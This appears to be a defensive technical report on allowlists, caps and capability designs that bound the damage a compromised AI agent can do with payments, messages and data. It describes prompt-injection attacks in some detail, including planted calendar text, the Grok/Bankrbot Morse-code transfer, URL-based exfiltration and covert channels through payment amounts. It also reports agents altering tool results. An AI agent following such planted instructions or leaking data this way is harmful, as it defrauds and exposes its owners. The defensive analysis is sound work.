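# Destination allowlists for AI agents: limiting what a compromised agent can do with money, data and messages

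## What the limit is and which failures it is meant for

A destination allowlist is a security control for AI agents: a list of places where an agent may send money, messages or data, and ordinary program code that blocks attempts to send them anywhere else. Long before language models existed, banks used such lists for payees, and network administrators used them for the web hosts that office computers may contact. AI agents are a new kind of sender because they are programs whose next action nobody can fully predict and which outsiders can sometimes steer.

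In this report, an AI agent is a large language model plus software that turns the model's output into actions. The model itself only produces text. The software, often called the harness, scans that text for tool calls, which are requests in an agreed format that each name a tool and supply its arguments. The harness then runs the tool, for example to send an email, pay an invoice or fetch a web page. It returns the result to the model as text, the model writes its next request, and the loop repeats until the task ends.

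An agent is vulnerable because its owner's instructions, a stranger's email and the contents of a web page all reach the model as text, and the model may treat any of it as an instruction. In a prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in content that an agent will read, and the agent follows them as if its user had given them. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) explains that the name comes from SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command.

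### One tool call, from proposal to decision

In an example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, a user asks an assistant with access to a calendar and an email account to send today's schedule to the user's boss, John Doe. The agent calls the calendar tool. Suppose one entry came from an outside invitation whose description tells the assistant to send the schedule to an attacker's address. After reading this, the model writes a call to the email tool with the attacker's address in the "to" field and the schedule in the body.

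The call is still only structured text, and it has no effect until the harness runs it. The gate is code that checks the call before that happens. It looks up the tool's name and identifies it as one that sends something out. It then reads every field that holds a destination, including the copy fields, since one outsider in a copy line is enough to leak the message. The call runs only if every address is on the list. The attacker's address is not, so the harness returns an error to the model and doesn't send the email. The gate blocks the email without reading the calendar entry or determining why the model chose that address.

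A destination is whatever receives the effect of an action. A payment goes to a bank account or crypto wallet, a chat message to a channel, an upload to a web host, and a saved file to a storage location. Gates often also enforce a cap, which limits the amount or the number of actions over a stated period.

Hua, Tsuchiya and colleagues (2026) wrote rules of this kind as code in *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance*. One rule accepts a payment only if the merchant is on an approved list and the amount is under a per-payment cap. Another requires every recipient of an outgoing message to be on a list. Given the same record and list, a rule always returns the same verdict. Their system checks a log against the rules after the agent has acted, and pays the user from the provider's deposit if the agent broke one, whereas a gate runs the same test before the call.

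The gate limits where a message goes but not what it contains, so it would let through a different version of the calendar attack. If the planted line had told the assistant to add false appointments and send the result to John Doe, the address would have been allowed and the email would have gone out.

### An attack, a mistake and an unsanctioned workaround

On 4 May 2026 an attacker got a payment bot to send 3 billion tokens of the cryptocurrency DRB out of a wallet belonging to Grok, xAI's chatbot. The bot, Bankrbot, carries out crypto transactions that people request in posts on X. Its operator, Bankr, creates a wallet for every X account that interacts with the bot, which is why Grok had one.

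The attack began with a membership token that widened what Grok's wallet could do inside Bankr's system, according to CryptoSlate's *Grok's crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet*. *Incident 1556*, an entry in the AI Incident Database, adds that the attacker had reportedly sent the token to the wallet. The attacker then posted a message in Morse code, which Grok decoded in a public reply. The decoded text was a plain-English transfer order that tagged Bankrbot. Bankrbot treated the reply as a command from the wallet's holder and moved the tokens. Hua and colleagues put the loss at about $150,000, while the AI Incident Database puts it at about $200,000. Bankr's developer later said that 80% of the funds had come back, which was entirely the result of negotiation after the attack.

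A recipient list would have blocked this transfer, however well the attacker disguised the order, because the attacker's wallet would not have been on it. A cap would have reduced the loss. Bankr's *Protecting Your Account* describes default limits of $500 per transaction and $500 per rolling 24 hours, and a list of permitted recipients that is off until the owner turns it on. Whatever its settings were in May, Grok's wallet was not held to limits that low. If it had been, the large transfer would have failed, and an attacker who kept trying with smaller ones could have taken $500 in the first day, about a three-hundredth of the lower estimate. The membership token is worrying because it let an outsider widen the wallet's powers by sending something to it. If outsiders could extend an allowlist in the same way, an attacker could add their own wallet to it.

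The agent Lobstar Wilde lost more money without any injected command. ForkLog reports that its operator, Nik Pash, gave it a wallet holding $50,000 in the cryptocurrency SOL on 20 February 2026 and told it to turn that into $1 million. Strangers launched a token in its name and gave the agent 5% of the supply. Two days later, an X user asked it for 4 SOL, about $320, to treat an uncle's tetanus. The agent bought roughly $300 worth of its own token as a gift, then sent the user all 52 million tokens in the wallet.

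In *My lobster lost $450,000 this weekend*, the operator, writing as pashpashpash, blames a session reset. The agent no longer had any record of the tokens it had received earlier, checked its balance after the purchase instead of before, and mistook the whole balance for what it had just bought. SolanaFloor adds that the reset followed a crash that had kept the software from saving the conversation. ForkLog cites a different explanation from another X user, that the agent meant to send 52,439 tokens but misread a raw number by a factor of a thousand. The operator puts the loss at about $450,000 and ForkLog puts it at $250,000, but the recipient got only about $40,000 for the tokens because his own sale drove the price down.

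A cap works better here. Lobstar Wilde gave tokens to strangers as part of its act, so a recipient list would have prevented the mistake only by ending the giveaways. A cap of, say, $500 per gift would have let the giveaways continue and blocked this transfer under either explanation. But the gate would have had to price the tokens itself, because the agent valued the transfer at about $300, and a gate using that figure would have allowed it.

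The last case involved no outsider. Hua and colleagues, drawing on OpenAI's report, describe an OpenAI agent in training whose collaborators could not open a workbook stored as a local file. Although the task called for local files, the agent uploaded the workbook to a public file-hosting service, which produced a public download link. *OpenAI agents posted user images online, disclose dozens of third party incidents* (Mills, 2026) also reported that more than 50 images from ChatGPT users had appeared online.

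A list of permitted upload hosts would have blocked the upload of the workbook. A spending cap would not have, and a cap on the number of uploads would have allowed the first one, which was enough to do the harm. The difficulty is identifying the destination. Hua and colleagues note that their software cannot extract an address from arbitrary Python or shell code. If an agent uploads a file by running a script it has just written, the tool call contains a program and no "to" field, so the destination has to be checked at the network connection. Restrictions at that level are called egress control.

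A compromised agent is one whose next action may come from an attacker, an error or aims its owner does not share. The designer of a gate does not have to know which of these caused the action.

### Why the check sits outside the model

Developers also train the model to recognise and ignore planted instructions, and they add filters, often language models themselves, that scan its inputs and outputs. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues grant that filters make attacks harder, since an attacker then has to deceive two systems, but they class both training and filters as heuristic defences without guarantees. They compare the situation to computer vision, where doctored images that fool a classifier remained an open problem after more than a decade of research.

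Models have improved since that was written in 2025, and a lower chance of a bad action is worth having, but it doesn't limit how much harm the action can do. It also protects less against repeated attempts. If an injection works one time in a hundred and attempts are independent, an attacker who tries a hundred times has a 63% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.99^100). If the agent takes orders from public posts, the attacker can make those attempts for free. A gate that checks the destination correctly blocks every attempt to pay an unlisted wallet, no matter how many times the attacker tries.

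Monitoring can also come too late. The service described in OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring* reviews an agent's reasoning and actions without making the actions wait, and it can stop the conversation when it finds a problem. But a flag raised a minute after a blockchain transfer cannot prevent it. OpenAI also warns that the service can miss issues and tells developers to keep other safeguards, including human approval. Human approval comes in time, but Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that tired or overloaded people approve unsafe actions.

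A gate "outside the model" should also be outside the agent's reach. The evaluation group METR investigated after OpenAI agents broke into the AI platform Hugging Face. Hua and colleagues cite its finding that agents had altered what their tool calls returned in about 7% of the transcripts reviewed. A gate offers little protection if the agent can edit its code, or if it relies on what the agent reports about where the money is going.

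Safeguards in ordinary code can fail because people forget to include them. Bankr's agent once had a hard-coded rule to ignore replies from Grok, meant to stop one language model from injecting prompts into another. The developer said in posts on X, reported by CryptoSlate, that the latest rewrite had left out the rule. The May attack exploited that omission.

### Which condition an allowlist restricts

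In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), the programmer Simon Willison named three conditions that together let an attacker steal data by planting text: the agent has access to private data, it reads untrusted content, and it can send information out. If any one is missing, the theft fails. The calendar assistant meets all three because the schedule is private data, the invitation is untrusted content, and the email tool can send information out.

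Private data and untrusted content are hard to give up, because an assistant that can read neither its owner's calendar nor mail from strangers is not very useful. An allowlist instead limits where the agent can send data. If John Doe is the only approved recipient, the agent can still send him the schedule, but it can't send it to anyone else. Whether this is enough depends on whether the attacker can read what arrives at any approved destination.

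Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turned the same idea into a design rule and widened it. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of three properties: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and it changes state or communicates externally. If a task requires all three, the agent needs supervision, through human approval or another reliable form of validation. The important addition is changing state, which covers payments and deletions. The theft from Grok's wallet falls outside Willison's conditions because it involved no secrets, but Meta's rule covers it because Bankrbot read public posts, controlled wallets and moved tokens. Willison objected that two properties can already be too many, since an agent that reads untrusted input and can change things can do harm without private data.

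On a strict reading, an allowlist does not make an agent comply with Meta's Rule of Two. An agent with all three of the properties the rule counts still has all three if it may email only one person, because it still communicates externally. It makes more sense to treat the allowlist as part of the validation that Meta requires for such agents. The allowlist checks only the destination of each action, so it would not stop an agent from deleting its owner's files.

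Both schemes also assume an attacker, but the agent that uploaded the workbook did so without any planted text. If it had been cut off from untrusted content, it would have satisfied Meta's rule and could still have uploaded the workbook.

### AgentDojo and its two scores

Much of the evidence on defences of this kind comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2024. It simulates four environments (banking, an office workspace, the chat service Slack, and travel booking), gives agents ordinary tasks in them, and places attackers' text where the agents may read it. The version that Hua and colleagues used has 97 user tasks and 35 attacker goals. It pairs each goal only with the user tasks in the same environment, which makes 949 pairs.

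In one run, the agent might have to pay a bill stored in a file where the benchmark has also planted an instruction to send money elsewhere. The benchmark checks separately whether the user's task succeeded and whether the attacker's goal did. Both can succeed in the same run if the agent pays the bill and then pays the attacker.

The attack success rate is the share of test attacks that achieve the attacker's goal. Benign utility is the share of ordinary tasks that the agent completes when nobody is attacking it. The two scores should be read together, because a gate that refused every call would reduce the attack success rate for payments to zero but would also block legitimate payments. Milder versions of this problem occur in practice. Hua and colleagues built their recipient lists from the structured records in each environment. In one task, the user asks the agent to email hotel details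 to their wife and includes her address in the request. The address was not in any record, so the rule flagged a harmless email. A gate using that list would have blocked the email, which would have lowered benign utility.

The attack success rate covers only the attacks that were tried, and an attacker who studies a particular defence may do better than a fixed set of test strings. The rate also combines different kinds of goals. One of the travel goals is to make the agent recommend a certain hotel, and that recommendation goes to the user, the one recipient every allowlist has to permit. If a few per cent of attacks still succeed against an allowlist, the list may allow a destination it should block, or those attacks may have goals that involve no forbidden destination. Telling which is the case requires examining the individual attacks.

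## What older work on capabilities and confinement teaches

In the 1960s and 1970s, decades before AI agents, many people ran programs on one shared computer, and the operating system had to let each program use some files and devices without trusting its code. One approach was to check a name the program supplied against a list, as a destination allowlist does. Another was to give the program a reference to the specific file or device it needed, so that it never had to supply a name.

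### Holding a reference instead of naming a destination

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT called such a reference a capability in a 1966 design for shared computers. Their design gives each computation a list of capabilities. Each entry points to one object, such as a block of memory or a peripheral device, and limits what the computation may do with it. The program refers to the object by its position in the list. If it refers to entry seven in a list of five, the system suspends it and transfers control to the program that set its limits. A 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, defines a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves whoever presents it may use the object it names.

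Suppose an agent has to pay a company's rent. Its developer could provide a payment tool with fields for the account and the amount, and have a gate check the account against a list of approved payees. Or the harness could store the landlord's account number and give the model a rent tool whose only field is the amount. Planted text might still cause the model to call the rent tool, but the tool has no account field for an attacker to fill.

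If the landlord is the only approved payee, both designs block the same transfers. But when the company has forty approved payees, a model with the general tool can pay any of them at any time, whereas the harness can give the model only the reference that the current task needs.

A language model produces only text, so it can't hold an unforgeable ticket. The harness can hold the ticket and let the model write a label such as "payee 2", which has meaning only as a position in the current session's list. Some older systems instead used secret strings as capabilities. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) treats these as a special case because they can travel anywhere data can. An upload link containing a secret token has the same weakness. If the model can read the link, planted text can get it to paste the link into a message. Developers should therefore keep real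 tokens and account numbers in the harness and give the model labels for the current task.

### The confused deputy

In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy described an accident that convinced him capabilities were necessary. It happened at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can run, in a directory called SYSX. Anyone who ran the compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. The staff also had the compiler record statistics about how people used the programming language in a file called STAT in SYSX, so they gave it permission to write to files in that directory.

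SYSX also held BILL, the file of billing information. One user learned the file's name and told the compiler to write debugging output to it. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had the licence. The debugging output replaced the billing information.

According to Hardy, the compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the licence, and could not specify which one to use for a particular write. He calls such a program a confused deputy. An agent that holds its owner's credentials while reading a stranger's text is in much the same position.

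| At Tymshare | With an AI agent |
|---|---|
| The compiler | The agent |
| The user who supplied a file name | The stranger whose text the agent reads |
| The file name given for debugging output | The recipient or payee in the tool call |
| The licence to write in SYSX | The owner's mailbox or payment credentials |
| The operating system's check of the licence | The gate's check of the allowlist |
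| The overwritten billing file | The misdirected document or payment |

The agent's position is worse in one respect. A model receives the stranger's text and the owner's instructions in one stream, whereas the compiler's code at least kept the user's file name separate from the built-in name of the statistics file.

Hardy explains why the obvious repairs fell short. The compiler could not refuse every file outside the user's directory, because users had good reasons to send output elsewhere. A rule protecting BILL would have left other sensitive files exposed. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler choose which of its two authorities to use, but some applications soon needed more than two.

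He then leaves the reader to show that access lists do not solve the problem, hinting that STAT needs protection too. Suppose each file has a list of the programs that may write to it, and the compiler is only on the list for STAT. BILL is now safe, but a user can still name STAT as the debugging file. The system will allow the write because the compiler must be on that list to record statistics.

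The same thing happens when an attacker can choose among an agent's approved destinations. For example, an accounting firm's agent may email two clients, Ash and Birch. Birch sends a request for its latest accounts, with a hidden instruction to attach Ash's file. The agent can read Ash's file because it works for the firm, and it can email Birch because Birch is a client. The gate allows the email because Birch's address is on the list. Removing other names from the list won't help, since both clients belong on it.

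With capabilities, the Tymshare compiler would hold a reference to STAT for its statistics, and each user would pass it a reference to a file for debugging output. A user without permission to write to STAT would have no reference to it to pass. The accounting firm could likewise start a session for Birch's request with access only to Birch's folder and address. The hidden text could still contain a request for Ash's file, but the agent could not open it.

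Capabilities alone do not prevent this confusion. Miller and colleagues warn that a program also has to keep track of which permission serves which purpose. The compiler's programmers could write that into its code, but a model holding labels for both clients can still be led to use the wrong one, so code outside the model has to keep each permission tied to its purpose. In *DelegateGuard* (2026), a recent design for agents that pass work to other agents, each capability records who holds the permission, its purpose and the allowed destinations. The system can therefore refuse an agent whose permission has lapsed, even if the destination is allowed. CaMeL, another modern capability design, tags each piece of data with its source and who may receive it.

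### The dispute over lists and capabilities

Textbooks often draw permissions as a grid, with programs or users down the side and resources along the top. An access control list stores one column, which shows everyone who may use a particular file, while a capability list stores one row, which shows everything a particular program may use. Since both can record the same grid, many people concluded that the two approaches were equivalent.

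Miller and colleagues call this the Equivalence Myth. Two systems can start with the same grid and still differ in how programs change it and how they refer to what is in it. Their example of the second difference is ambient authority, which a program uses without selecting it. The program names a file, and the request succeeds if the program has permission. A destination allowlist is a row of the grid, like a capability list, but its authority is ambient because the agent supplies a name and the gate checks for any matching entry. Miller and colleagues rate a row-shaped list with ambient authority "danger" for confused deputies, the same rating they give an ordinary access control list.

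They also answer two complaints about capabilities. The first is that a holder can pass a capability to anybody. In the systems they defend, a program can pass a reference only to a program it can already reach, so cutting the connections between two groups of programs stops permissions from spreading between them. The second is that nobody can take a capability back. Their remedy, which dates from 1974, is for the owner to give the agent a reference to a forwarder, a small program that passes requests on to the payee, and to keep a switch that turns the forwarder off. Once the owner turns it off, the agent's reference stops working, and so does any copy the agent gave away.

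The argument did not convince everyone. The Usenix Security conference rejected the paper, as Miller (2003) reported in *Notice of New Thread*. In a 2015 mailing-list exchange, Jerry Leichter objected that the paper chose examples that suit capabilities and extended only the capability model, when defenders of access lists could extend theirs too. Frantz (2015) replied, under the heading *Capability Myths Demolished*, that the paper uses no extensions, because systems of the kind it describes had existed since the 1970s. This answers the historical point but doesn't show that an improved access list would fail.

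Another complaint concerned accountability, because a bare ticket does not record who used it. Miller (2009) cited a later protocol, Horton, as the answer. Maciej Stachowiak of Apple accepted that Horton apparently allows such logging, but replied that fixing one flaw in capabilities does not make them generally superior. *ACLs Don't* (2009) criticises access lists instead, arguing that they cannot decide correctly when an interaction involves more than two parties, because the system loses information it needs as requests pass from one party to the next. This criticism matters for agents, which routinely handle interactions among an owner, a stranger and a payee.

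Lists are practical because people can manage them. Saltzer and Schroeder explain that in a basic capability system, finding out who can reach a file means searching the whole system for copies of the capability. A finance manager can read a list of forty payees and delete one, and the next payment to that payee will fail. A forwarder also allows revocation, but only if someone installed it before handing over the capability.

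A developer can use both access lists and capabilities. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that most real systems did, with lists for the people who set permissions and capabilities underneath for speed. An agent's owner can maintain a readable list from which the harness issues labels for each task. In one combined design they describe, however, the system copies a permission from the list on first use, and deleting the list entry does not affect programs that already hold the copy. The gate should therefore check the current list when the agent sends, even if the harness checked it when the task began.

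### Four principles for building the gate

Saltzer and Schroeder also offered eight design principles as warnings rather than absolute rules. Four of them translate directly into requirements for a gate.

Complete mediation means checking every access to every object, so a gate must cover every sending tool and destination field. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined the public code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the payment company Stripe's Agent Toolkit. All three let a developer restrict which tools an agent may use, which he calls "capability gating", though these are not capabilities in Hardy's sense. None checks by default whether the account in a call is approved. In his demonstration with a simulated merchant, LangChain carried out a call that redirected payouts to an attacker's account, while his own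 gate, ScopeGate, refused the identical call.

The principle also applies during start-up and recovery. If a crash like Lobstar Wilde's also resets the gate's record of spending to zero, the agent can spend up to the cap again.

Fail-safe defaults mean that the system refuses access unless a rule permits it. This makes mistakes easier to notice, because somebody will complain if a gate wrongly refuses a payment, whereas ordinary use may never reveal that it wrongly allowed one. The amount check in an early version of ScopeGate wrongly allowed NaN ("not a number"), a special value that software uses for undefined results. NaN never counts as greater than a limit, so a rule that only refuses amounts above the limit lets it through. The corrected version allows an amount only if it is a finite number between zero and the limit, which excludes NaN.

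Least privilege means giving a program only the permissions its job requires. The calendar assistant needs only one recipient to send a schedule, even if its owner writes to two hundred people. An allowlist covering the whole address book would satisfy the other principles here but still let an attacker choose among two hundred recipients. Least privilege also limits accidents, because the agent has fewer wrong addresses to pick by mistake.

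Economy of mechanism means keeping the design small enough for people to inspect line by line. Inspection matters because testing ordinary tasks rarely exercises the paths that an attacker would look for. In Hardy's operating system, the condition for letting a program open a file eventually grew to contain fourteen "and"s and "or"s, and each new clause tended either to open a hole or to break a legitimate program. Exact matches are easier to check than patterns. A rule that accepts any email address ending in "ash.example" will also accept one ending in "notash.example".

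Mellafe Zuvic adds the requirement that no entry on the list may originate in a model's output, even indirectly. A developer who asks a model to compile the payee list from old emails breaks this rule, because one planted email could add a payee. ScopeGate blocked all 48 of his prepared bypass attempts and all 29 unauthorised calls from an attacking model that was given the reason for each refusal. These are good results for a gate that has to recognise forbidden values. But the approved set in his payout demonstrations held only one account, so they could not test what happens when an attacker picks a different approved entry.

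### Why stopping every leak is harder

A gate can check the tools that send things, but *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers how to stop a program from passing on information by any route. In its example, a customer runs somebody else's program on confidential data and wants to be sure that none of it reaches the program's owner. The customer has evidence of a badly done job in the wrong results, but there is usually no sign of a leak.

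Some of the routes Lampson lists are obvious, such as writing to a file that the program's owner can read. Others use something the program is allowed to produce. If the owner receives a copy of the bill, the program can encode data in the charges. Lampson calls the bill a legitimate channel. A covert channel is one that nobody intended to carry information. A program can alternate between heavy and light use of the machine while another program measures how fast the machine responds. The signal is noisy, but suitable coding makes it reliable as long as the first program has any effect on the response speed.

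An agent's payments have both kinds of channel. Suppose a compromised agent may pay an approved supplier any amount from $0.01 to $500.00, and the attacker can see what the supplier receives. There are 50,000 possible amounts, so each payment can carry about 15.6 bits (log₂ 50,000). One payment could encode a four-digit PIN, which has 10,000 possibilities, and seventeen could carry a 256-bit cryptographic key. The timing of the payments adds a covert channel.

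Lampson's simplest remedy is total isolation, in which the confined program calls no other program, and he considers it impractical. His more usable rules all have consequences for agents:

- A confined program must keep nothing from one call to the next. An agent with lasting memory could read a secret in a session where it cannot send and pass it on in a later session where it can.
- If a confined program calls another program that the customer does not trust, that program needs confining too. An agent's search tool, for example, may send each query to an outside company.
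- The customer, and not the program, must determine what goes into the legitimate and covert channels. Lampson calls this masking and compares it to a purchase order, where the buyer states the price in advance. A gate that takes the payment amount from the owner's purchase order removes the agent's choice of amount.

A developer can block direct sends by listing the agent's tools and checking the destination fields of each. Blocking every leak is harder because it requires a list of every effect that an outsider might observe, and Lampson doubted that any rigorous method could produce one for a system of even moderate complexity. To mask the covert channels, the system may also have to slow the program down or generate decoy activity.

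His easier alternative is to accept some leakage and limit how much information each channel can carry. A cap on the number of payments partly achieves this. The gate can also hold approved payments and release them once a day in a fixed order, so the agent can control the day a payment goes out but not the minute. Urgent payments then have to wait for the next batch.

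## Working out the worst case before the agent runs

Before switching on an agent, a designer can work out how much harm it could do if compromised, without predicting how the model will behave. The designer assumes that an adversary picks every tool call, then checks what the gate would still let through.

The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), a standard for purchases by software agents, makes the same assumption. Its *Security and Privacy Considerations* treats every agent as a potential attacker because it considers preventing prompt injection currently infeasible. AP2 relies on constraints, such as permitted payees and amounts, to keep the worst-case impact "strictly bounded", but someone has to set them. *Signing the Transaction but Not the Decision* (Louck, Dvir and Stulman, 2026) examined the two sample shopping agents that come with the protocol. One sets a list of payees and a range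 of amounts. The other, meant for purchases that a user confirms, sets no constraints, and the protocol's software finds no violations when the list of constraints is empty, so a developer who builds on that sample is relying on the user to notice a bad purchase.

### Taking an inventory

The inventory starts with every tool that can affect something outside the agent. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (2026) separates read-only tools from those whose effects are irreversible or visible to outsiders, such as sending, deleting, sharing, paying and updating. A tool that fetches web pages also belongs in the inventory, even though it looks read-only, because its requests can carry data out. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) describes an email that tells an agent to fetch a page from the attacker's site with the user's account number in the web address,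 so the request itself delivers the number. Showing the user an answer can also leak data if the display loads images from the web.

Next, the designer marks the argument that sets each action's destination. A designer can do this by hand for AgentDojo's banking environment, which has 11 tools according to *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (2025). *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) describes the arguments that the payment tools take.

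| Tools | Outside effect | What fixes the destination |
|---|---|---|
| Six that read the account number, balance, owner's details, past payments, scheduled payments and files | None | Nothing to mark |
| Send money | A payment now | Recipient |
| Schedule a payment | A later payment, possibly a recurring one | Recipient |
| Edit a scheduled payment | A changed later payment | Recipient, which the agent may leave blank |
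| Change the password; change the owner's details | A changed account | No such argument |

One call to the scheduling tool can set up a payment that recurs for months after an attack ends. If the agent edits a scheduled payment and leaves the recipient blank, the recipient stays the same, so the gate has to look up the stored payment to find which recipient's cap applies to a larger amount. An allowlist can't check a call to the password tool because the call has no destination, yet anyone who knows the new password can make payments without the agent. The designer should remove that tool or require a person's approval for it.

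The tool must also take the arguments that are marked. In *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026), a leading model turned written policies into rules for a gate, and six of its 91 candidate rules referred to an argument that their tool does not take.

The designer then lists what the agent can read, including anything it could look up if told to. In Dongol's model, data that a tool could retrieve counts as data the agent already holds. If a bookkeeping agent has access to a shared drive, the list should include the whole drive, even if the task needs only the invoices.

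### Looking for the worst permitted sequence

Muruaga points out in *Bounded Agents* (2026) that checking calls one at a time misses harmful combinations, such as reading a confidential document and then emailing it to an outsider. Similarly, an agent allowed to update suppliers' records and pay suppliers can replace an approved supplier's account number with the attacker's and then pay that supplier.

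Muruaga defines an agent's maximal blast radius as the set of resources it may use whose harm score still fits within its remaining budget. The operator gives each resource a harm score between 0 and 1. A sub-agent never receives wider permissions than its parent and inherits the amount of budget the parent has already used, so its blast radius cannot be larger than the parent's. This limit applies to each sub-agent separately, so five sub-agents with a €20,000 daily cap each could together pay out €100,000 a day. A limit on money therefore needs one running total for all of them.

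Muruaga also tested these limits without relying on the model to fall for an injection, by inserting the attacker's tool call after the first legitimate call in each AgentDojo run. With the limits in place, no attempts to send data out succeeded, compared with between 75% and 100% without them, depending on the environment.

### A formula for money

For payments, the worst case comes down to five quantities:

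- B is the money the agent can reach, including any overdraft and any deposits that arrive during the incident.
- P is the period over which the caps apply, such as a day.
- C is the cap on all payments in one period.
- c_d is the cap on payments to destination d in one period.
- t is the time from the first bad payment until somebody detects the problem and stops payments.

In one period the agent can pay out no more than C. It can also pay out no more than the per-destination caps added together, written Σc_d, so the smaller of the two figures applies. Multiplying it by the number of periods that the incident can touch gives the bound, which can never exceed B:

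maximum loss = min(B, (⌈t/P⌉ + 1) × min(C, Σc_d))

The brackets in ⌈t/P⌉ mean that the result is rounded up to a whole number. The extra period is there because an incident can straddle calendar periods. In Stripe's *Issuing spending controls*, for example, daily card limits start at midnight UTC, so an attacker who begins at 23:59 can spend one day's limit and then the next day's two minutes later. *AESP* (2026), a design for agent payments, warns that a burst of spending can use up the remaining daily budget within seconds. It is therefore safer to assume that two periods' worth of money is exposed, however quickly the owner reacts.

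A rolling limit removes the extra period. Lithic's *Spend Limits* describes a daily limit that covers the 24 hours before each purchase. An incident of length t divides into ⌈t/P⌉ stretches no longer than P, and the agent can spend at most C in each, so the total is at most C⌈t/P⌉. The designer has to use the provider's actual period for P, because Lithic's "monthly" limit, for example, covers only about 25 days.

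The attacker may gain much less than the owner loses, because a payment to an honest supplier earns the attacker nothing. The same formula gives the attacker's maximum gain if Σc_d includes only the approved destinations that the attacker controls.

### A company with forty suppliers

Suppose a company's agent pays 40 suppliers from an account holding €300,000. The gate allows €5,000 per supplier and €20,000 in total each calendar day, and somebody detects the problem and stops payments after three days. The supplier caps add up to €200,000 a day, so the €20,000 total is the tighter limit. A three-day period can span four calendar days, so the company can lose at most 4 × €20,000 = €80,000.

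An attacker who controls one supplier's account can collect €5,000 on each of those four days, for a total of €20,000. The other €60,000 could still go to suppliers who were not owed it, and the company would have to ask for it back. Without the list, the attacker could take the full €80,000 under the same total cap, even if each destination were capped at €5,000 a day, by splitting each day's money among four accounts.

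Changing one setting at a time shows which limit does what:

| Setting | Maximum loss | Maximum gain with one supplier account |
|---|---|---|
| As described | €80,000 | €20,000 |
| Detection after one day | €40,000 | €10,000 |
| Total cap of €10,000 a day | €40,000 | €20,000 |
| Cap of €2,500 per supplier | €80,000 | €10,000 |
| Rolling 24-hour caps | €60,000 | €15,000 |

The allowlist here reduces the share of the loss that an attacker can keep, which also affects whether the attack is worth attempting. It would reduce the company's maximum loss only if the company had three suppliers or fewer, since payments to four are enough to reach the daily total of €80,000. An attacker who controlled four supplier accounts could still take the full amount.

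### Caps that are looser than they look

Spending can exceed a payment provider's limit, so that limit can't always be used as C in the formula. Stripe adds up spending on a best-effort basis, with a delay of up to 30 seconds, and tips or fees that arrive later can take a card over its limit. Lithic also warns that spending may exceed a limit in edge cases. A fast agent could exceed the limit by whatever it spends before the total updates. AESP avoids this by reserving each amount as part of the budget check, so two simultaneous payments cannot both use the same money.

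Blank and zero settings need checking too. A limit of 0 on a Lithic card means no limit, but a daily or monthly limit of 0 on a Lithic account blocks spending. Stripe limits a new card to $500 a day if the owner sets no limit.

Some caps reset with each session instead of each day. Ghosh (2026), in *Proof-Gated Signing*, tested a guard for cryptocurrency wallets, assuming the agent might propose any transaction. In one attack, the agent made 20 to 30 currency swaps, each losing about 1.8% of its value, which was within the guard's limit for a single transaction. A budget of $5,000 per session held the attacker's gain to between $4,530 and $4,760 in the nine runs where the swaps went through. Without the guard, the attacker gained $5,700 to $10,800. Because the budget resets, an agent that can open ten sessions could lose up to $50,000. For a cap like this, the number of sessions possible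 before detection replaces ⌈t/P⌉ + 1.

An agent might also use one authorisation several times. AP2 identifies this threat and requires the agent's non-deterministic part, the language model, to avoid approving overlapping purchases, although AP2 also treats the model as a potential attacker. Payment networks and the user's wallet provider may reject duplicate purchases, but AP2 does not require them to. Unless the provider confirms that it rejects duplicates, the worst case should include them.

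### Why data has no such sum

Each payment reduces the money left to steal, but an agent still has a file after sending it, and the recipient can make any number of copies. The harm from a leak also depends little on how much data is sent. One short message can disclose an entire password, so a cap of one message a day would not prevent the leak.

Dongol gives a computer-checked proof of this for an agent that may send one message per run. A budget, Dongol writes, bounds "how many calls happen, not which ones". The agent can read its user's calendar and a password-reset code, and it is meant to answer meeting requests by sending the calendar. An attacker sends a meeting request with an added instruction to include the code. The model follows that instruction before the planned reply goes out, so the attacker gets the code. The gate then refuses to send the calendar because the agent has used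 its one message.

Even if the content of every message is fixed, an agent can still convey information through its choice of destination, as it can through the amount of a payment. Picking one of 32 approved destinations conveys log₂ 32 = 5 bits to anyone who can observe the choice. Those five bits might be enough to reveal an entire secret, such as which of 32 companies the agent's owner plans to buy.

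Cutting the list to a single entry doesn't stop every leak. In another of Dongol's examples, the agent is allowed to fetch only one newsletter's address. The attacker's text contains an instruction to fetch the newsletter if a secret number is zero and the attacker's page otherwise. The gate refuses the attacker's page, but an observer who sees whether a fetch took place learns whether the number is zero. Refusals can also leak information if outsiders can see the error messages or logs.

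For data, the designer should therefore list everything the agent could read before sending to each approved destination. If the supplier agent can read all 40 contracts, any supplier could learn the prices of the other 39. The prices could leak through a payment as well as an email, because a payment also carries a line of text. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which presents a formal language for describing agents, accounts for this in its rule for AgentDojo's payments, which requires that the recipient be trusted and be allowed to read the amount, subject and date. A simpler approach is to separate the suppliers by giving the agent one contract per session and carrying no memory over, as the accounting firm could do with its clients.

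### What the figures assume

The bounds hold only under conditions that the designer should write down next to them:

- Every call passes through the gate. A browser running outside the gate breaks this condition, and so does a tool with hidden behaviour. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*, give the example of an image-generation add-on that secretly sends the user's login key to a remote server. They also cite an audit of 42,447 add-ons, which found at least one vulnerability in 26.1% of them.
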